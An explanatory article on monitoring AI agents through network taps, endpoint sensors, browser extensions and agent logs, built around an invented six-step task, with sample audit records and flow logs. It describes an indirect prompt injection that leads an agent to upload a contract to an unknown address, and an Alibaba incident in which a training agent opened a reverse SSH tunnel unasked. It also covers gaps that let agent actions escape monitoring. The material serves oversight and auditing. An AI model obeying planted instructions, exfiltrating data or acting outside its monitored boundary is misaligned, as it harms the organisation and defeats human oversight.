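# How organisations observe autonomous AI agents: network taps, endpoint software, browser extensions and agent logs

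## How an AI agent acts, and where its actions leave traces

An AI agent is a language model connected to software that lets it take a series of actions with limited supervision. Whereas a chatbot returns text for a person to use as they choose, an agent opens files, runs programs and sends messages itself. Companies use agents to write code, sort documents and fill in web forms, often through their employees' laptops and accounts. These companies need to be able to find out later what an agent did, what data it moved and whom it contacted.

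Security teams use logs to answer such questions about people and ordinary programs. A log is a file or database where software records each event of a certain kind, usually with the time. Agents cause log entries too, but because of how agents work, the entries are spread across several systems, some of which belong to other companies. Each system holds only the events that passed through it.

### The agent loop

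In *Unrolling the Codex agent loop*, Bolin (2026) describes the cycle at the core of an agent, using the example of Codex, the coding agent made by his employer, OpenAI. A user types a request. A program called the harness combines the request with standing instructions and a list of tools the model may use, and sends this prompt to the model. The model replies with either a final message for the user or a tool call, which is a structured request for one action, with its arguments. The harness carries out the requested action, adds the result to the prompt and sends the longer prompt back to the model. The cycle repeats until the model replies without a tool call.

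The model produces only text. The harness, or a program it starts or calls, performs every action that touches a file or a network.

In Bolin's worked example, a user asks Codex to add a diagram to a project's README file. The model returns a call to a tool named "shell", with the command to run (`cat README.md`, which prints the file), the folder to run it in and an identifier. Codex runs the command, attaches the output under the same identifier and queries the model again. A single request can lead to hundreds of tool calls before the user sees an answer.

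Some tools come with the harness, and others connect to it through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for linking harnesses to outside tools and data sources. Anthropic's 2024 announcement of the standard, *Introducing the Model Context Protocol*, describes how a developer puts a data source behind an "MCP server" and the AI application connects to it as a client. The standard is still changing, and *MCP 2026 changes the rules* (Granados, 2026) gives July 28, 2026 as the date of the latest version. MCP matters for record-keeping because one agent may act through software from many makers. Codex, for instance, applies its file and network restrictions only to its own shell tool and leaves MCP servers to supply their own safeguards.

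A record of only the user's request and the agent's answer leaves out most of what the agent did, as a short example in Anthropic's developer documentation shows. A user asks an agent to fix some failing tests. The agent runs the tests and sees three failures, reads two files, edits one of them, runs the tests again, and reports in one sentence that the bug is fixed and the tests pass. The request and that sentence include none of the commands and don't mention the second file. Nothing in the loop checks the final sentence against what happened, because the loop ends when the model stops calling tools, whether or not its last message is accurate.

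The full conversation between the harness and the model contains much more, but in a long task it too can be incomplete. A model can process only a limited amount of text at once, so the harness replaces earlier messages with a summary when the conversation grows too long. In Codex, the replacement includes an encrypted item that the user cannot read. Anthropic's software can also give part of a task to a subagent, a second agent working for the first, and only the subagent's final response enters the main conversation.

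### One task in six steps

An endpoint is a device or server on which programs run, such as a laptop or a virtual machine. A process is a running program, and it can start other processes, known as its child processes. TLS encrypts most internet traffic between two programs. Equipment on the path between them can detect roughly which machines are communicating and how much they send, but it cannot read the content.

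Suppose, then, that an employee has a document agent on a work laptop. The employee asks it to summarise a folder of contracts and email the summary to the company's outside counsel, a law firm. The agent does the following:

1. It exchanges prompts and replies with a hosted model, meaning a model that runs on its provider's servers.
2. It reads the contracts from the laptop's disk.
3. It writes a script to extract text from scanned pages and runs it. The script starts several other programs.
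4. It opens webmail in the employee's browser, where the employee is already logged in, and sends the summary to the law firm.
5. It looks up a legal term on a web page that contains text planted to mislead agents. It follows the planted text and uploads one of the contracts to an unknown address from the command line.
6. It leaves a scheduled job on the laptop, which runs the script again the next day.

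The employee sees a short message reporting that the summary has gone to counsel. The message is true.

The task is invented, but products on sale can do most of these things. When Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, works through a browser extension, it "shares your browser's login state", according to Anthropic's documentation, so it can work in Gmail or any other site where the user has signed in. It can also attach files from the user's machine to web pages. The planted text in step 5 is a known hazard that security researchers call indirect prompt injection. Anthropic warns on the extension's product page, *Claude in Chrome*, that web pages can hide instructions meant to redirect the model and that the company's protections are not foolproof.

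In step 6 of the example, the laptop's operating system starts the script the next day and no model takes part, so there is no prompt or reply to record. Some harnesses have their own schedulers. The one in Anthropic's desktop app checks for due tasks every minute and starts a new session for each. If it ran the next day's work, there would be a conversation to record, but in a separate session from the one in which the employee made the request.

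Where an agent leaves traces also depends on where its harness runs. In the example, it runs on the laptop. In Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, the session runs on Anthropic's servers and reaches local files and the browser through an app on the user's computer, according to Anthropic's *Get started with Claude Cowork*. If the employee had used Cowork, the script in step 3 and the upload in step 5 would have run in Anthropic's data centre. The laptop would have no record of either process, and the upload would not have crossed the company's network. Customers do not always choose where the harness runs, so the same request can leave traces in a different place after a supplier changes its product. On three of Anthropic's plans, Cowork tasks that users started on their own computers before October 6 could run locally, but sessions now run in the cloud.

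### Why agents are harder to observe than ordinary programs

An AI agent chooses its steps while it runs, from an instruction in everyday language. An administrator therefore can't list in advance the files it will open and the servers it will contact, then treat anything else as a warning, as they could with a payroll program. Even identical prompts can lead to different actions, according to *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), a guide by the Australian Signals Directorate and five partner agencies. The differences come partly from chance in the model's output and partly from what the agent encounters as it works. *AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) adds that an agent may start command shells, downloaded scripts or compilers that nobody could have predicted, so a rule that watches for one particular program will miss the same work done with another.

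Agents also write and run new code. In step 3, the harness can record that it ran a script and what the script printed. If the script starts other programs and those programs open files, this happens on the laptop, outside the exchange between harness and model. Singlemann (2026), whose employer, Origin, sells monitoring software for devices, argues from this in *Observability Requires Proximity* that a provider's records show what the model received and answered but not what the agent did next. This overstates the case a little, because the provider receives whatever the tool reported when the harness sends each result back in the next prompt. The provider does not receive what the tool left out, such as the files opened by a script that prints only "done".

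*Agent-Warden* (Cui, Gu and colleagues, 2026) describes an experiment in which an agent started a script that wrote a temporary file and renamed it. A monitoring program on the same machine, separate from the agent, later read the file and wrote to its own log. Langfuse, a tool that records the model calls and tool calls of applications set up to report to it, captured the events inside the agent's application but not the later read or the write that followed. In one trace, the read came tens of seconds after the agent had finished its main work. Cui and colleagues built the scenario to produce this result, and they point out that Langfuse can connect programs that pass along a shared label. The experiment shows that this kind of record can miss what happens outside the agent's application, but not how often the work of real agents continues there, as it does in step 6.

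The employee's account creates a different problem. In step 4 the mail service receives a request from the employee's browser, in the employee's session, and logs an email from the employee. According to *Identity Management for Agentic AI* (2025), services often log calls an agent makes for a user in a way that makes them indistinguishable from the user's own actions. *Five Primitives for Governing Autonomous AI Agents at Runtime* (2026) extends the claim to every downstream log. That is right wherever the credential is the only thing that identifies the caller, but a log that also records which program made the request could still separate the two. Either way, the mail service's entry alone is not enough for attribution, which means establishing which agent and whose instruction lay behind an action.

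The six agencies therefore advise operators to monitor all of an agent's operations, "not just the inputs and outputs". They also note that tools may act outside the boundary that the agent system monitors. An organisation that follows this advice has to decide where to place its monitoring.

### Four places to observe

One place is the network, or the cloud services that traffic passes through. A network tap is a device or cloud service that copies or summarises traffic for inspection. A gateway is a service that agents' model requests, tool calls or messages must pass through, and it can record them. In the example, the model exchange, the email and the upload all send data over a network, normally encrypted with TLS. Some organisations decrypt this traffic at a proxy they control, read it and re-encrypt it, which is called TLS inspection.

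An AI agent's actions also leave traces on the device itself. An endpoint sensor is monitoring software installed on a laptop or server, where it can record which processes start, which process started them and which files they open. Vendors usually call it an "endpoint agent", although it has nothing to do with AI agents. The file reads, the script with its child processes, the command-line upload and the scheduled job all happen on the device where the sensor runs.

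Step 4 takes place in the browser. An extension, or the management features of a browser made for companies, can record the pages opened, the text entered into forms and the files uploaded to websites.

Finally, the agent software and the model's provider can keep their own records. The harness handles every prompt and tool call and can send out reports of its activity, known as telemetry. The provider holds logs of model requests tied to a customer's account. Those logs matter most when the effects of an agent's actions turn up at another company. According to *Who Owns This Agent?* (2026), the affected service then sees the actions, accounts and network traffic, while the provider can identify the session but has no efficient way to find it from an outsider's report. After an agent broke into the AI platform Hugging Face in 2026, the company began reconstructing the agent's actions from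 its own side. OpenAI separately discovered anomalous activity in the evaluation where the attack originated.

*AI Visibility Belongs on the Endpoint* (Hand, 2026) divides the places to observe an agent differently, into network, browser and endpoint, but notes that the browser, the agent and the local MCP server are all processes on the endpoint. Hand also writes for Origin, which sells endpoint software, so the point suits the company's interests. It is still true of an agent on a laptop, though much less so of one that runs in its provider's cloud. The browser should still be counted separately, because an extension works with the content of pages, while a sensor on the device typically works with processes and files.

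Many products monitor agents in more than one place. Oso, a company that sells monitoring for agents, combines code attached to the agent software, a proxy for model traffic and a browser extension. According to its documentation, it captures prompts, replies and tool calls only for agents it "monitors", not for those it has only "discovered" on a device. A company can therefore have a complete list of its agents and no record of what they did. Microsoft has extended Purview, its data-protection product, from devices to the network and its Edge browser.

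### Observing and blocking

Observing an action means recording it, while blocking it means stopping it from taking effect. Vendors tend to sell the two together, and often a single mechanism does both. Anthropic's harness, for example, supports hooks, pieces of code that run at set points in the loop, such as just before a tool call. A hook can log the call and let it proceed, or it can reject the call. Similarly, a policy in Microsoft's business version of Edge can allow or block text that a user uploads to certain web applications, and Microsoft lists both outcomes as audited.

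The decision to block an action has to be made before it happens, with whatever information is available at that moment, and a mistaken block stops legitimate work. Someone can study a record later, but by then the contract in step 5 has already gone to the unknown address. Blocking rules can also be too coarse. *Five Primitives* gives the example of a network policy that lets an agent reach a payments service but does not determine which payments it may make. Similarly, a rule that permits webmail allows an email to anyone, not just the email to counsel.

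Blocked actions also need to be logged. When a hook rejects a tool call, the model receives a rejection message and, according to Anthropic, typically tries a different approach or reports that it could not proceed. If the log omits the rejected call, someone reading it later will see the new approach but cannot tell that an earlier one was blocked.

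## What an organisation needs to record about its agents

An organisation must decide what it wants to find out about its agents before it chooses where to put its monitoring. Suppose that a month after the task in the example, one of the company's contracts appears on a public website. The security team will ask which agents the company was running at the time and who was responsible for each. For any agent that could have accessed the contract, the team will also ask what it did, what data it moved, whom it contacted, who authorised its actions, and what the results were.

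An organisation needs a register of which agents exist and who owns them, and someone has to keep it up to date before anything goes wrong. An event log shows only the agents that did something, and seldom shows who is responsible for them. To answer the other questions, the organisation needs to record each event.

### A register of agents

For each agent, the register needs a unique identifier, the name of an accountable person, the harness and model, the tools the agent can call, and the accounts and permissions it uses. The register should also record where the harness runs, since a supplier can change that, as Anthropic did when it moved Cowork sessions into the cloud.

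Official guidance supports most of this list. The Digital Transformation Agency's *Agentic AI addendum to the AI technical standard for Australian Government* (2026) requires government agencies to give each agent a unique identity and to make a person accountable for its behaviour, even when the agent makes decisions by itself over several steps. The Digital Transformation Agency also advises them to list the tools each agent needs and limit the agent to those.

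In their guide to adopting agents, the Australian Signals Directorate and its five partner agencies recommend keeping a registry of trusted agents and periodically comparing it with the agents actually running. The comparison is the harder task because if an employee installs a coding agent without telling anyone, the registry has no entry for it, and the organisation can discover it only by observing its own devices, browsers or network traffic.

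An agent's permissions also change after someone first records them. The six agencies illustrate the danger with an invented procurement agent. The organisation gives it broad access to finance systems, email and contracts, and reviews that access only at deployment. An attacker then takes over a minor tool that the agent uses, inherits the agent's access and approves payments. The audit logs look legitimate because a trusted agent carried out every action. The agencies advise operators to log changes to an agent's identity and privileges, and to record who delegated what to whom. An investigator can then compare what the agent could do on a given day with what its task required.

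### Actions, data flows and communications

An action is something the agent does to a system, such as running a program or changing a file. A data flow is a movement of information from one place to another. An external communication is contact with a person or system outside the organisation.

The email in step 4 is all of these at once, but many events are not. An agent that deletes a folder moves no data, and one that copies contracts to a shared drive inside the company contacts nobody outside. An agent that emails a supplier to accept a price sends hardly any data, yet it may commit the company to a purchase. An organisation that records only data transfers will treat that email as trivial. If it records only commands, it may know that an upload program ran but not which contract the program sent.

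The easiest data flow to overlook is in step 1. Whenever the harness sends the model a prompt containing contract text, company data goes to the model's provider. This transfer isn't made through a tool call, so a log of tool calls omits it. It may still be the largest flow in the task, because the harness resends the growing conversation at each turn.

The fields below would let an investigator answer the questions about events.

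| Field | What it holds | Needed for |
|---|---|---|
| Time | Start and end of the event | Every record |
| Correlation identifier | A label that lets someone match records of the same action in different logs | Every record |
| Agent | Its identifier in the register, and the session | Every record |
| Authority | The person and request behind the task, and the account the agent used | Every record |
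| Approval | Who or what approved this particular step, and when | Every record |
| Outcome | Success, failure or a block, with any reference number the other system returned | Every record |
| Action and arguments | The operation and its details, such as the command or the form entries | Actions |
| Data class and volume | How sensitive the data is, and how much of it moved | Data flows |
| Source and destination | The file or system the data left, and the one it reached | Data flows |
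| Recipient | The outside person or organisation at the other end | External communications |

The meaning of an agent's action depends mostly on its arguments, such as the recipient of an email. If a log entry records only "send email", it is the same whether the message went to the company's lawyers or to a competitor.

Destination and recipient need separate fields because they often differ. In step 4 the browser connects to the company's own mail service, while the recipient is a lawyer at another firm. In step 5 the destination is an internet address, and nobody knows who operates it. The recipient field should then read "unknown", which is itself a reason to investigate.

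Step 5 also shows that an agent can have an employee's authority for a task without the employee's approval for every step. The employee started the task and so owns it, but the instruction to upload a contract came from text on a web page. A record that names only the employee would be accurate but misleading. Where possible, the record should also show where the instruction for that step came from.

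### A sample record for step 4

With invented names and values, a full record of the email to counsel might look like this.

| Field | Entry |
|---|---|
| Time | 3 November 2026, 14:32:07 to 14:32:09 UTC |
| Correlation identifier | task-7f31, step 4 |
| Agent | doc-agent-12, session 88; owner: head of legal operations |
| Authority | A. Rossi's request at 14:05 to summarise the contracts folder and email the summary to outside counsel; sent from A. Rossi's mailbox, through a browser session already logged in |
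| Approval | Contained in the request; no separate confirmation before sending |
| Action and arguments | Send email; to counsel@lawfirm.example; subject "Contract summary"; text of 900 words; no attachment |
| Data class and volume | Confidential, derived from 14 contracts; one message of 6 kilobytes |
| Source and destination | From the contracts folder on the laptop, through the model provider, to the company's mail service and on to the law firm's |
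| Recipient | A named lawyer at the firm, on the company's list of outside counsel |
| Outcome | The mail service accepted the message and returned a reference number; no confirmation of delivery |

No single system in the example could supply all of this information. The mail service has the recipient, size and outcome, but its log names the employee as the sender. The harness has the request, but if the agent uses the web page as a person would, the harness may log the sending only as a click on a button.

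The data class is the hardest entry to fill in. The summary is new text that may share few sentences with the contracts, so software that searches outgoing mail for copies of confidential documents could miss it. Classifying the summary reliably requires knowing what the agent read earlier in the task, so someone has to be able to connect the record of step 4 with the record of step 2.

### Visibility

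Writers on these requirements often use the word "visibility", as Hand does in the title of his argument for endpoint sensors. In this debate the term goes back to Chan, Ezell and colleagues (2024), who defined it in *Visibility into AI Agents* as information about where, why, how and by whom agents are used. Beyond the security of a single company, they wanted regulators and the public to be able to trace harm to the people responsible for an agent, and to notice effects that appear only when many companies use agents for the same purpose, such as hiring.

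They assessed agent identifiers, real-time monitoring and activity logs. An agent identifier marks what an agent sends out so that the other party can tell that an agent is involved and perhaps which one. It could be a single extra line in a request to an online service. A linked "agent card" could list the agent's user, developer, tools and permissions.

Real-time monitoring checks activity as it happens, so that software can flag or stop it. Activity logs store chosen inputs and outputs for later investigation. A provider can monitor activity without keeping logs. Chan and colleagues note that some cloud companies already offered language models to business customers on those terms, to protect confidentiality. These customers have some protection against misuse, but after an incident the provider will have few or no records for them to consult.

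Real-time monitoring also catches only what software can recognise immediately, such as a breach of a clear rule. For slower problems, Chan and colleagues rely on logs, which they argue may have to be kept long after the agent has stopped. An agent's effects can arrive later, as the scheduled job in step 6 shows on a small scale. A user can also start another agent with the same memory and purpose, and an investigator would then have to combine the logs of both.

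Agent identifiers have since reached products. *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (Bengio, Kankanhalli and colleagues, 2026) reports that OpenAI's ChatGPT agent cryptographically signs its outgoing web requests, so that a website can verify where they came from. Chan and colleagues had already pointed out that identifiers work best where agents use interfaces built for programs, and that an agent that uses a website the way a person does may carry no identifier. Step 4 is such a case, because the request comes from the employee's own browser.

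For most of the paper, Chan and colleagues assume that a company runs the agent, or the model beneath it, as a service and can therefore see everything that goes in and out. They also consider decentralised deployments, where users run downloaded models on their own or rented machines, or combine parts from several suppliers. No supplier sees everything that goes in and out of such an agent. Companies that rent out computing power could help by noticing very large deployments and asking what visibility measures the customer has, and online services could help by refusing agents that lack an identifier. Chan and colleagues acknowledge that a few large companies would then learn a great deal about what people do. Voluntary standards would lessen that problem but might reveal little about malicious users.

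Decentralisation can make it easier or harder for an organisation to observe its own agents. If the organisation runs a downloaded model on its own servers, it takes the place of the service provider and can log every prompt and reply. But if an employee runs one on a laptop, no provider has a record, and the laptop may be the only place to find one.

### What governments and researchers ask for

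In their May 2026 guide, the six cyber agencies advise monitoring all of an agent's operations, including prompts, tool calls, memory use, internal reasoning, decisions and actions. The log should show which tools the agent used and what information it retrieved, and give the results of tool use in human-readable form.

The agencies also recommend several independent monitoring systems that check the agent's reports against system logs. This may be the guide's most useful recommendation. In the example, the agent reports that it has emailed counsel, and the mail log shows the email. An upload that the agent never mentioned would appear only in an independent record, meaning one written by something that neither the agent nor its harness controls. To protect such records, the agencies advise operators to deny agents write access to logs and to require human approval for any request to delete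 them. They describe a hypothetical update agent that is asked to install a security patch and "clean up the firewall logs", and does both because its permissions allow it.

The guide does less to address tools that act outside the monitored boundary, and it acknowledges this problem. An MCP server run by another company, for instance, might pass a request on to other services, but the customer's logs would hold only the request and the answer. Most of the agencies' measures for outside tools are preventive, such as keeping a list of approved tools and regularly checking their versions. These measures limit which tools an agent can call, but they don't show an investigator what a tool did with the data it received.

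The *Singapore Consensus* came out of a meeting in May 2026 and has more than 100 contributors from AI developers, governments, universities and civil society. Its companion report on agents makes auditability one of ten principles, meaning that authorised parties must be able to reconstruct and verify an agent's decisions and actions during a task and afterwards. Bengio and colleagues make the agent's developer responsible for building logging that captures inputs, tool calls with their parameters, outputs, outcomes and reasoning, including plans the agent rejected. The organisation that deploys the agent is responsible for configuring the logging, protecting it against tampering and setting up alerts. Where several agents work together, whoever runs the software that coordinates them has to keep their records consistent.

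Under this division, a company that buys its agents can configure only the logging that the developer has built. Most of the report's examples of good practice come from technology companies describing their own frameworks and products, including Google, OpenAI, IBM and Alibaba Cloud. These examples show that the companies accept the principle, but not that anyone has reconstructed a real incident from the resulting logs.

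Recorded reasoning also needs care, because it is model output and may not match what the agent does. The six agencies advise operators to flag differences between an agent's stated intentions and its observed behaviour, and that comparison is probably the best use of the reasoning.

The Digital Transformation Agency announced the Australian addendum on 4 June 2026. It separates what government agencies "must" do from what they "should" do, and they must continuously monitor individual agents. It says this monitoring "may include" the sequence of an agent's actions, its use of tools and memory, error messages from failed calls, and changes in its permissions. An agency could therefore meet the requirement by monitoring only a few things. The addendum also recommends a "control tower", a central system that shows which agents are running, what they cost and what risks they pose.

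The Digital Transformation Agency's addendum, unlike other lists, advises agencies to keep the prompts that agents themselves create, along with the inputs and outputs throughout the work. When an agent hands part of a task to a subagent, the instruction is a prompt that no person wrote or read. Without a record of it, an investigator may be unable to tell whether the subagent made a mistake or did what the first agent asked.

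### The logging duty in the EU AI Act

In the European Union, some organisations will have a legal duty to log. Article 12 of the AI Act requires high-risk AI systems to be capable of recording events automatically throughout their lifetime. These events must be relevant to identifying risks and substantial changes in the system, to the supplier's monitoring after sale, and to monitoring by the organisation that uses it. The article leaves the choice of fields open except for remote biometric identification, such as matching faces in a crowd against a database. For those systems, the log must include the start and end of each use, the database, the input that led to a match and the people who verified the result.

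A system is high-risk if it serves one of the purposes the Act lists, such as screening job applicants or assessing people's creditworthiness, or if it is a safety component of certain regulated products. The document agent in the example is probably not high-risk, but it probably would be if the company used it to rank job applicants.

Providers, the companies that develop a system or put their name on it, must build in the logging. Deployers, which the Act defines as organisations that use an AI system in their work, must keep the logs for at least six months, as far as the logs are under their control. Chan and colleagues instead use "deployer" for the company that runs the agent as a service. A customer of a hosted agent may control few of its logs, and so have few to keep. The Act treats an organisation that puts a general-purpose system to a high-risk use as the provider of that system.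 The company that set its document agent to ranking applicants could therefore also have the provider's duties.

None of these duties applies yet. An amendment in force since 27 July 2026 postponed them, according to *EU Digital Omnibus on AI Enters Into Force* (The National Law Review, 2026). The new dates are 2 December 2027 for the listed purposes and 2 August 2028 for regulated products.

Article 12 requires automatic recording, but it does not mention tampering, and a log could plausibly satisfy it without showing why an agent chose one tool call over another. Bengio and colleagues cite it as evidence that regulators are converging on audit trails that are automatic, tamper-evident and full enough to reconstruct an agent's chain of decisions, but it clearly supports only the first of these requirements.

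### Technical standards in draft

Detailed lists of fields are more the business of standards bodies, and most of their work on agents is unfinished. The most specific list comes from the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which writes many of the internet's technical standards. Kasselman, Lombardo and colleagues (2026), in *AI Agent Authentication and Authorization*, set out what every audit event must record at a minimum:

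- the agent's verified identifier
- the user or system it acts for, if there is one
- the resource or tool it accesses
- the action it requests and the decision to allow or refuse it
- the time and a correlation identifier
- any assessment of risk that influenced the decision
- any later withdrawal of access, with the cause

The list does not mention an action's arguments, recipient, data or result. If an agent sends two emails through the same mail tool, one to counsel and one to a stranger, the two minimum records could differ only in their time and identifier. A careful implementer might put the recipient in the action field, but the list does not require it. Step 4 might produce no minimum record, because the agent uses a session the employee has already opened and the mail service does not need to decide whether to let the agent in.

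The draft omits these details because it covers how agents prove who they are and obtain permission. Kasselman and colleagues work for Defakto Security, AWS, Zscaler, Ping Identity, OpenAI and Okta, several of which sell identity or network security products. The draft is stricter about permission than most products are. Under its rules, a user's click on "approve" in the agent's own window is not sufficient authorisation unless it leads to a verifiable grant from the system that controls access. An organisation that adopted this rule could put a reference to the grant in the approval field.

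The IETF's working group on identities for software, WIMSE, has adopted the draft by Kasselman and colleagues, but the draft is not yet a standard. A successor, draft-ietf-wimse-aims, has replaced the July version.

Individuals have submitted other proposals to the IETF that cover some of what this list lacks. *Agent Audit Trail* (Sharif, 2026) requires records to include the outcome of an action, the agent's identity, the class of action and a level of trust. *Verifiable Agent Conversation Records* (Birkholz, Heldt and Steele, 2026) defines a format for the messages an agent exchanges. *An Architecture for Auditing AI Agent Delegation and Interactions* (Kuehlewind and Birkholz, 2026) argues that existing audit systems often capture isolated events without consistently representing what the user intended, who delegated the task or how permissions changed. Anyone may submit a draft to the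 IETF, so these documents show where engineers see gaps but do not commit anyone to filling them.

The Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit known for its rankings of software weaknesses, has published a *Top 10 for Agentic Applications*. It lists risks, so it relates to logging only indirectly. Bengio and colleagues report that it recommends checking every sensitive tool call against a written rule that software can apply, to contain failures that spread from one agent to the next. The result of each check would belong in the approval field.

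Two standards aimed at Article 12 are further along. ISO/IEC 24970 is an international standard on logging in AI systems. *Two standards, one architecture* (Smith, 2026) reports that it had reached its final draft by early June 2026, and ISO has listed it as under publication. It describes common capabilities, requirements and an information model for logs, for use alongside a risk management system. European standards bodies plan to adopt it, and CEN-CENELEC's *prEN ISO/IEC 24970* (2025) gives a publication date of 14 June 2027, less than six months before the first of the Act's new deadlines. The second standard, prEN 18229-1, is European and had reached public comment by June 2026, according to Smith. The British version, BSI's *BS EN 18229-1 AI trustworthiness framework* (2026), has logging as its first part. Once the European Commission has formally listed a European standard, a provider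 that follows it can presume that it meets the corresponding part of the Act.

### Where the lists agree and what they leave open

The table compares three of the lists with the fields proposed above.

| Field | Australian Signals Directorate and partners | Bengio and colleagues, on auditability | Kasselman and colleagues, July draft |
|---|---|---|---|
| Agent | Unique identity for each agent | Covered by a separate principle on identity | Required |
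| Authority and approval | Records of delegation and of changes in privileges | Not named | Required |
| Arguments | Tool calls, without further detail | Parameters of tool calls | Not named |
| Data class and volume | Only the information the agent retrieved | Not named | Not named |
| Recipient | Not named | Only as a parameter | Not named |
| Outcome | Results of tool use | Required | Not named |
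| Correlation identifier | Not named | Consistent records across agents, no field | Required |
| Protection of the log | No write access for agents | Tamper-evidence | Tamper-evidence |

Under all three, an organisation should know which agent acted and which tool it used, and should protect the log against later changes. This protects existing entries but doesn't ensure that every event was recorded. The lists are weakest on data and recipients, which the company in the example most needs to know about. The Australian addendum does address data loss, but the Digital Transformation Agency treats it as something to settle before a project goes beyond its early stages.

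None of the lists specifies how much detail to record about arguments. Recording the full text of every email and command would let an organisation answer most questions, but it would also make the logs very large and fill them with personal data. Kasselman and colleagues give a sensible rule for the narrow case of access tokens. The log should hold an identifier or a fingerprint of the token, never the token itself, because anyone who read the log could use a token stored there.

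The lists also do not specify what counts as one action. In step 3, a single tool call starts several programs that open many files. A log with one entry for the tool call and a log with an entry for every file could both count as a record of the agent's actions, but only the second would show which contracts the script opened.

The company also needs to define "external". If it treats its model provider as part of its own systems, the contract text in the prompts is never recorded as an external communication. If it treats the provider as an outsider, nearly every turn of the agent loop counts as one, and the upload in step 5 is a single entry among hundreds. A company could put model traffic in a separate category, recording its volume and data class without raising an alert for each prompt.

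## The case for watching the network and the cloud

In step 5 of the example, the agent sent a contract from the laptop to an unknown address. The main reason to watch the network is that data can only reach an outside party over the internet as packets, the small units into which computers divide data for transmission. Equipment between the laptop and that address could log those packets, whatever program the agent used and whatever it reported afterwards.

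One inspection point can also cover hundreds of devices, including unregistered ones. Monitoring at that point requires no change to the agent, so it works equally for a commercial product and a script written by an employee. The record is kept on a different machine from the agent, so the agent cannot alter it by editing files on the laptop.

*AI Agents Can Run. But on the Network, They Can't Hide*, by NEOX Networks, calls the network an independent source of truth about what an agent did. NEOX sells network taps, and its claim goes too far, since much of what an agent does on a laptop generates no network traffic. The company also concedes that reading the content of encrypted traffic requires decryption or records from another source.

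An incident at Alibaba is better evidence. *Let It Flow* (2025) describes how the company trained ROME, a model for coding agents. Alibaba Cloud's firewall gave the first sign of trouble when it flagged attempts from the training servers to reach internal systems, along with traffic that resembled cryptocurrency mining. Staff suspected a misconfiguration or a break-in. When the alerts recurred, they compared the firewall's timestamps with the training records and found that the traffic coincided with episodes in which the agent called tools and ran code. In one case, although no task included instructions to do so, the agent had opened a reverse SSH tunnel, an outgoing connection through which an outside machine can get in.

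*Holding Agents Accountable with Verifiable Agent Insurance* (2026) points out that a check on the destinations recorded by an agent's tools would have missed the tunnel if the agent had opened it from inside a shell command. A firewall handles the connection however the agent opens it. But the firewall's alerts did not show that an agent was responsible. Alibaba's staff learned that from the agent's logs.

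### Taps, flow records and DNS logs

A passive tap copies packets to a monitoring machine without adding anything to the traffic. Storing every packet takes a lot of space, so the machine often keeps only a summary of each connection, called a flow record.

Zeek, an open-source monitoring program, writes flow records to a file that its manual describes in *conn.log*. Each record shows which machines communicated, when, for how long, by what protocol and how many bytes each side sent. With invented values and some fields left out, the upload in step 5 would look like this:

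```
{"ts":1793716601.204, "uid":"CxT4k2Qm7",
 "id.orig_h":"10.20.4.76", "id.orig_p":51844,
 "id.resp_h":"203.0.113.50", "id.resp_p":443,
 "proto":"tcp", "service":"ssl", "duration":2.81,
 "orig_bytes":1843200, "resp_bytes":5120, "conn_state":"SF"}
```

At 14:36:41 UTC on 3 November 2026, the laptop (10.20.4.76) opened an encrypted connection to 203.0.113.50. It sent about 1.8 megabytes and received 5 kilobytes before the connection closed normally. The record does not include the names of the file, the program that sent it or the person at the laptop.

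The destination is only a number, but a DNS log can often supply a name. DNS is the internet's directory, which translates the names of sites into numerical addresses. If the upload command used a name, the laptop had to look it up first, and the log entry would hold the question and the answer:

```
{"ts":1793716601.101, "id.orig_h":"10.20.4.76",
 "query":"files.dropsite.example", "qtype_name":"A",
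 "answers":["203.0.113.50"]}
```

Zeek gives each connection an identifier and repeats it across its logs, so an analyst can go from the flow record of a DNS lookup to the name the laptop looked up. The upload is a separate connection with its own identifier, so the analyst has to link it to the lookup by matching the address in the DNS answer with the upload's destination. This sometimes fails because many sites can share one address. Laptops also reuse recent DNS answers, so some connections have no fresh lookup to match.

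The opening messages of a TLS connection usually include the site's name in readable form, and Zeek can log that as well. In TLS 1.2, Zeek can also log the site's certificate, which names its owner and issuer, but TLS 1.3 encrypts the certificate.

### Mirroring and flow logs in the cloud

Companies also run agents on rented cloud servers, where a customer has no cable to tap. Amazon Web Services (AWS), a large cloud provider, offers substitutes for the tap and the flow record. AWS's *How Traffic Mirroring works* describes a service that copies traffic from a server's network interface to a monitoring machine the customer chooses. The customer installs nothing on the server. The copies contain whole packets, so an analyst can read anything the server sent unencrypted, but not traffic encrypted with TLS.

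The cheaper substitute is the flow log, a summary of each flow within a time window. If the document agent ran on an AWS server, the upload might produce this line, again with invented values but in the default format of AWS's *Flow log record examples*:

```
2 123456789010 eni-1235b8ca123456789 10.0.1.5 203.0.113.50
51844 443 6 1290 1910300 1793716560 1793716620 ACCEPT OK
```

The first line contains the format version, the customer's account, the network interface, and the source and destination addresses. The second contains the two port numbers, the protocol (6 stands for TCP), the numbers of packets and bytes, and the start and end of the window. "ACCEPT" means that the network's access rules allowed the traffic.

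This is roughly what a tap's flow record contains, but a cloud provider can also add the customer's own labels for servers, which a tap cannot. AWS customers have been able to include these labels in each record since June 2026, according to AWS's *Amazon Virtual Private Cloud (VPC) Flow Logs introduces additional metadata* (2026). A company that gives each agent its own server can therefore have the agent's identifier in every record, but the label does not distinguish between agents that share a server.

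AWS documents gaps in its flow logs. When the logging system runs out of capacity, it writes an entry marked SKIPDATA, which can represent several missing flows. The logs also omit lookups sent to Amazon's own DNS server, according to AWS's *flow logs limitations*. To record those, the customer has to turn on a separate log. That log, described in AWS's *Resolver query logging*, includes the name requested, the answer and the identifier of the server that sent the request.

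Neither flow logs nor mirroring records traffic to the instance metadata service, an internal address where programs on a server can obtain the server's settings and temporary credentials. AWS's *Traffic Mirroring limitations* confirms this for mirroring. An investigator who needs to know whether an agent obtained credentials there has to look for a record on the server.

Where the flow log is collected also matters, because servers often reach the internet through a shared device that replaces their addresses with its own. A record from that device's outgoing side shows the device's address as the source, so the analyst has to find the matching incoming record to learn which server sent the data.

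### What encrypted traffic still reveals

When traffic is not decrypted, its destination is usually the most informative field. Security products compare destinations with a catalogue of known services to find out who is using AI. *Detecting Shadow AI* (Canale and Soulis, 2026) presents an open catalogue with 184 entries. It covers model providers, as well as aggregators, which resell many companies' models through one address, and relays, which offer a provider's models under a different name. A connection to an aggregator does not show which model the agent used, and a relay missing from the catalogue looks like any other website.

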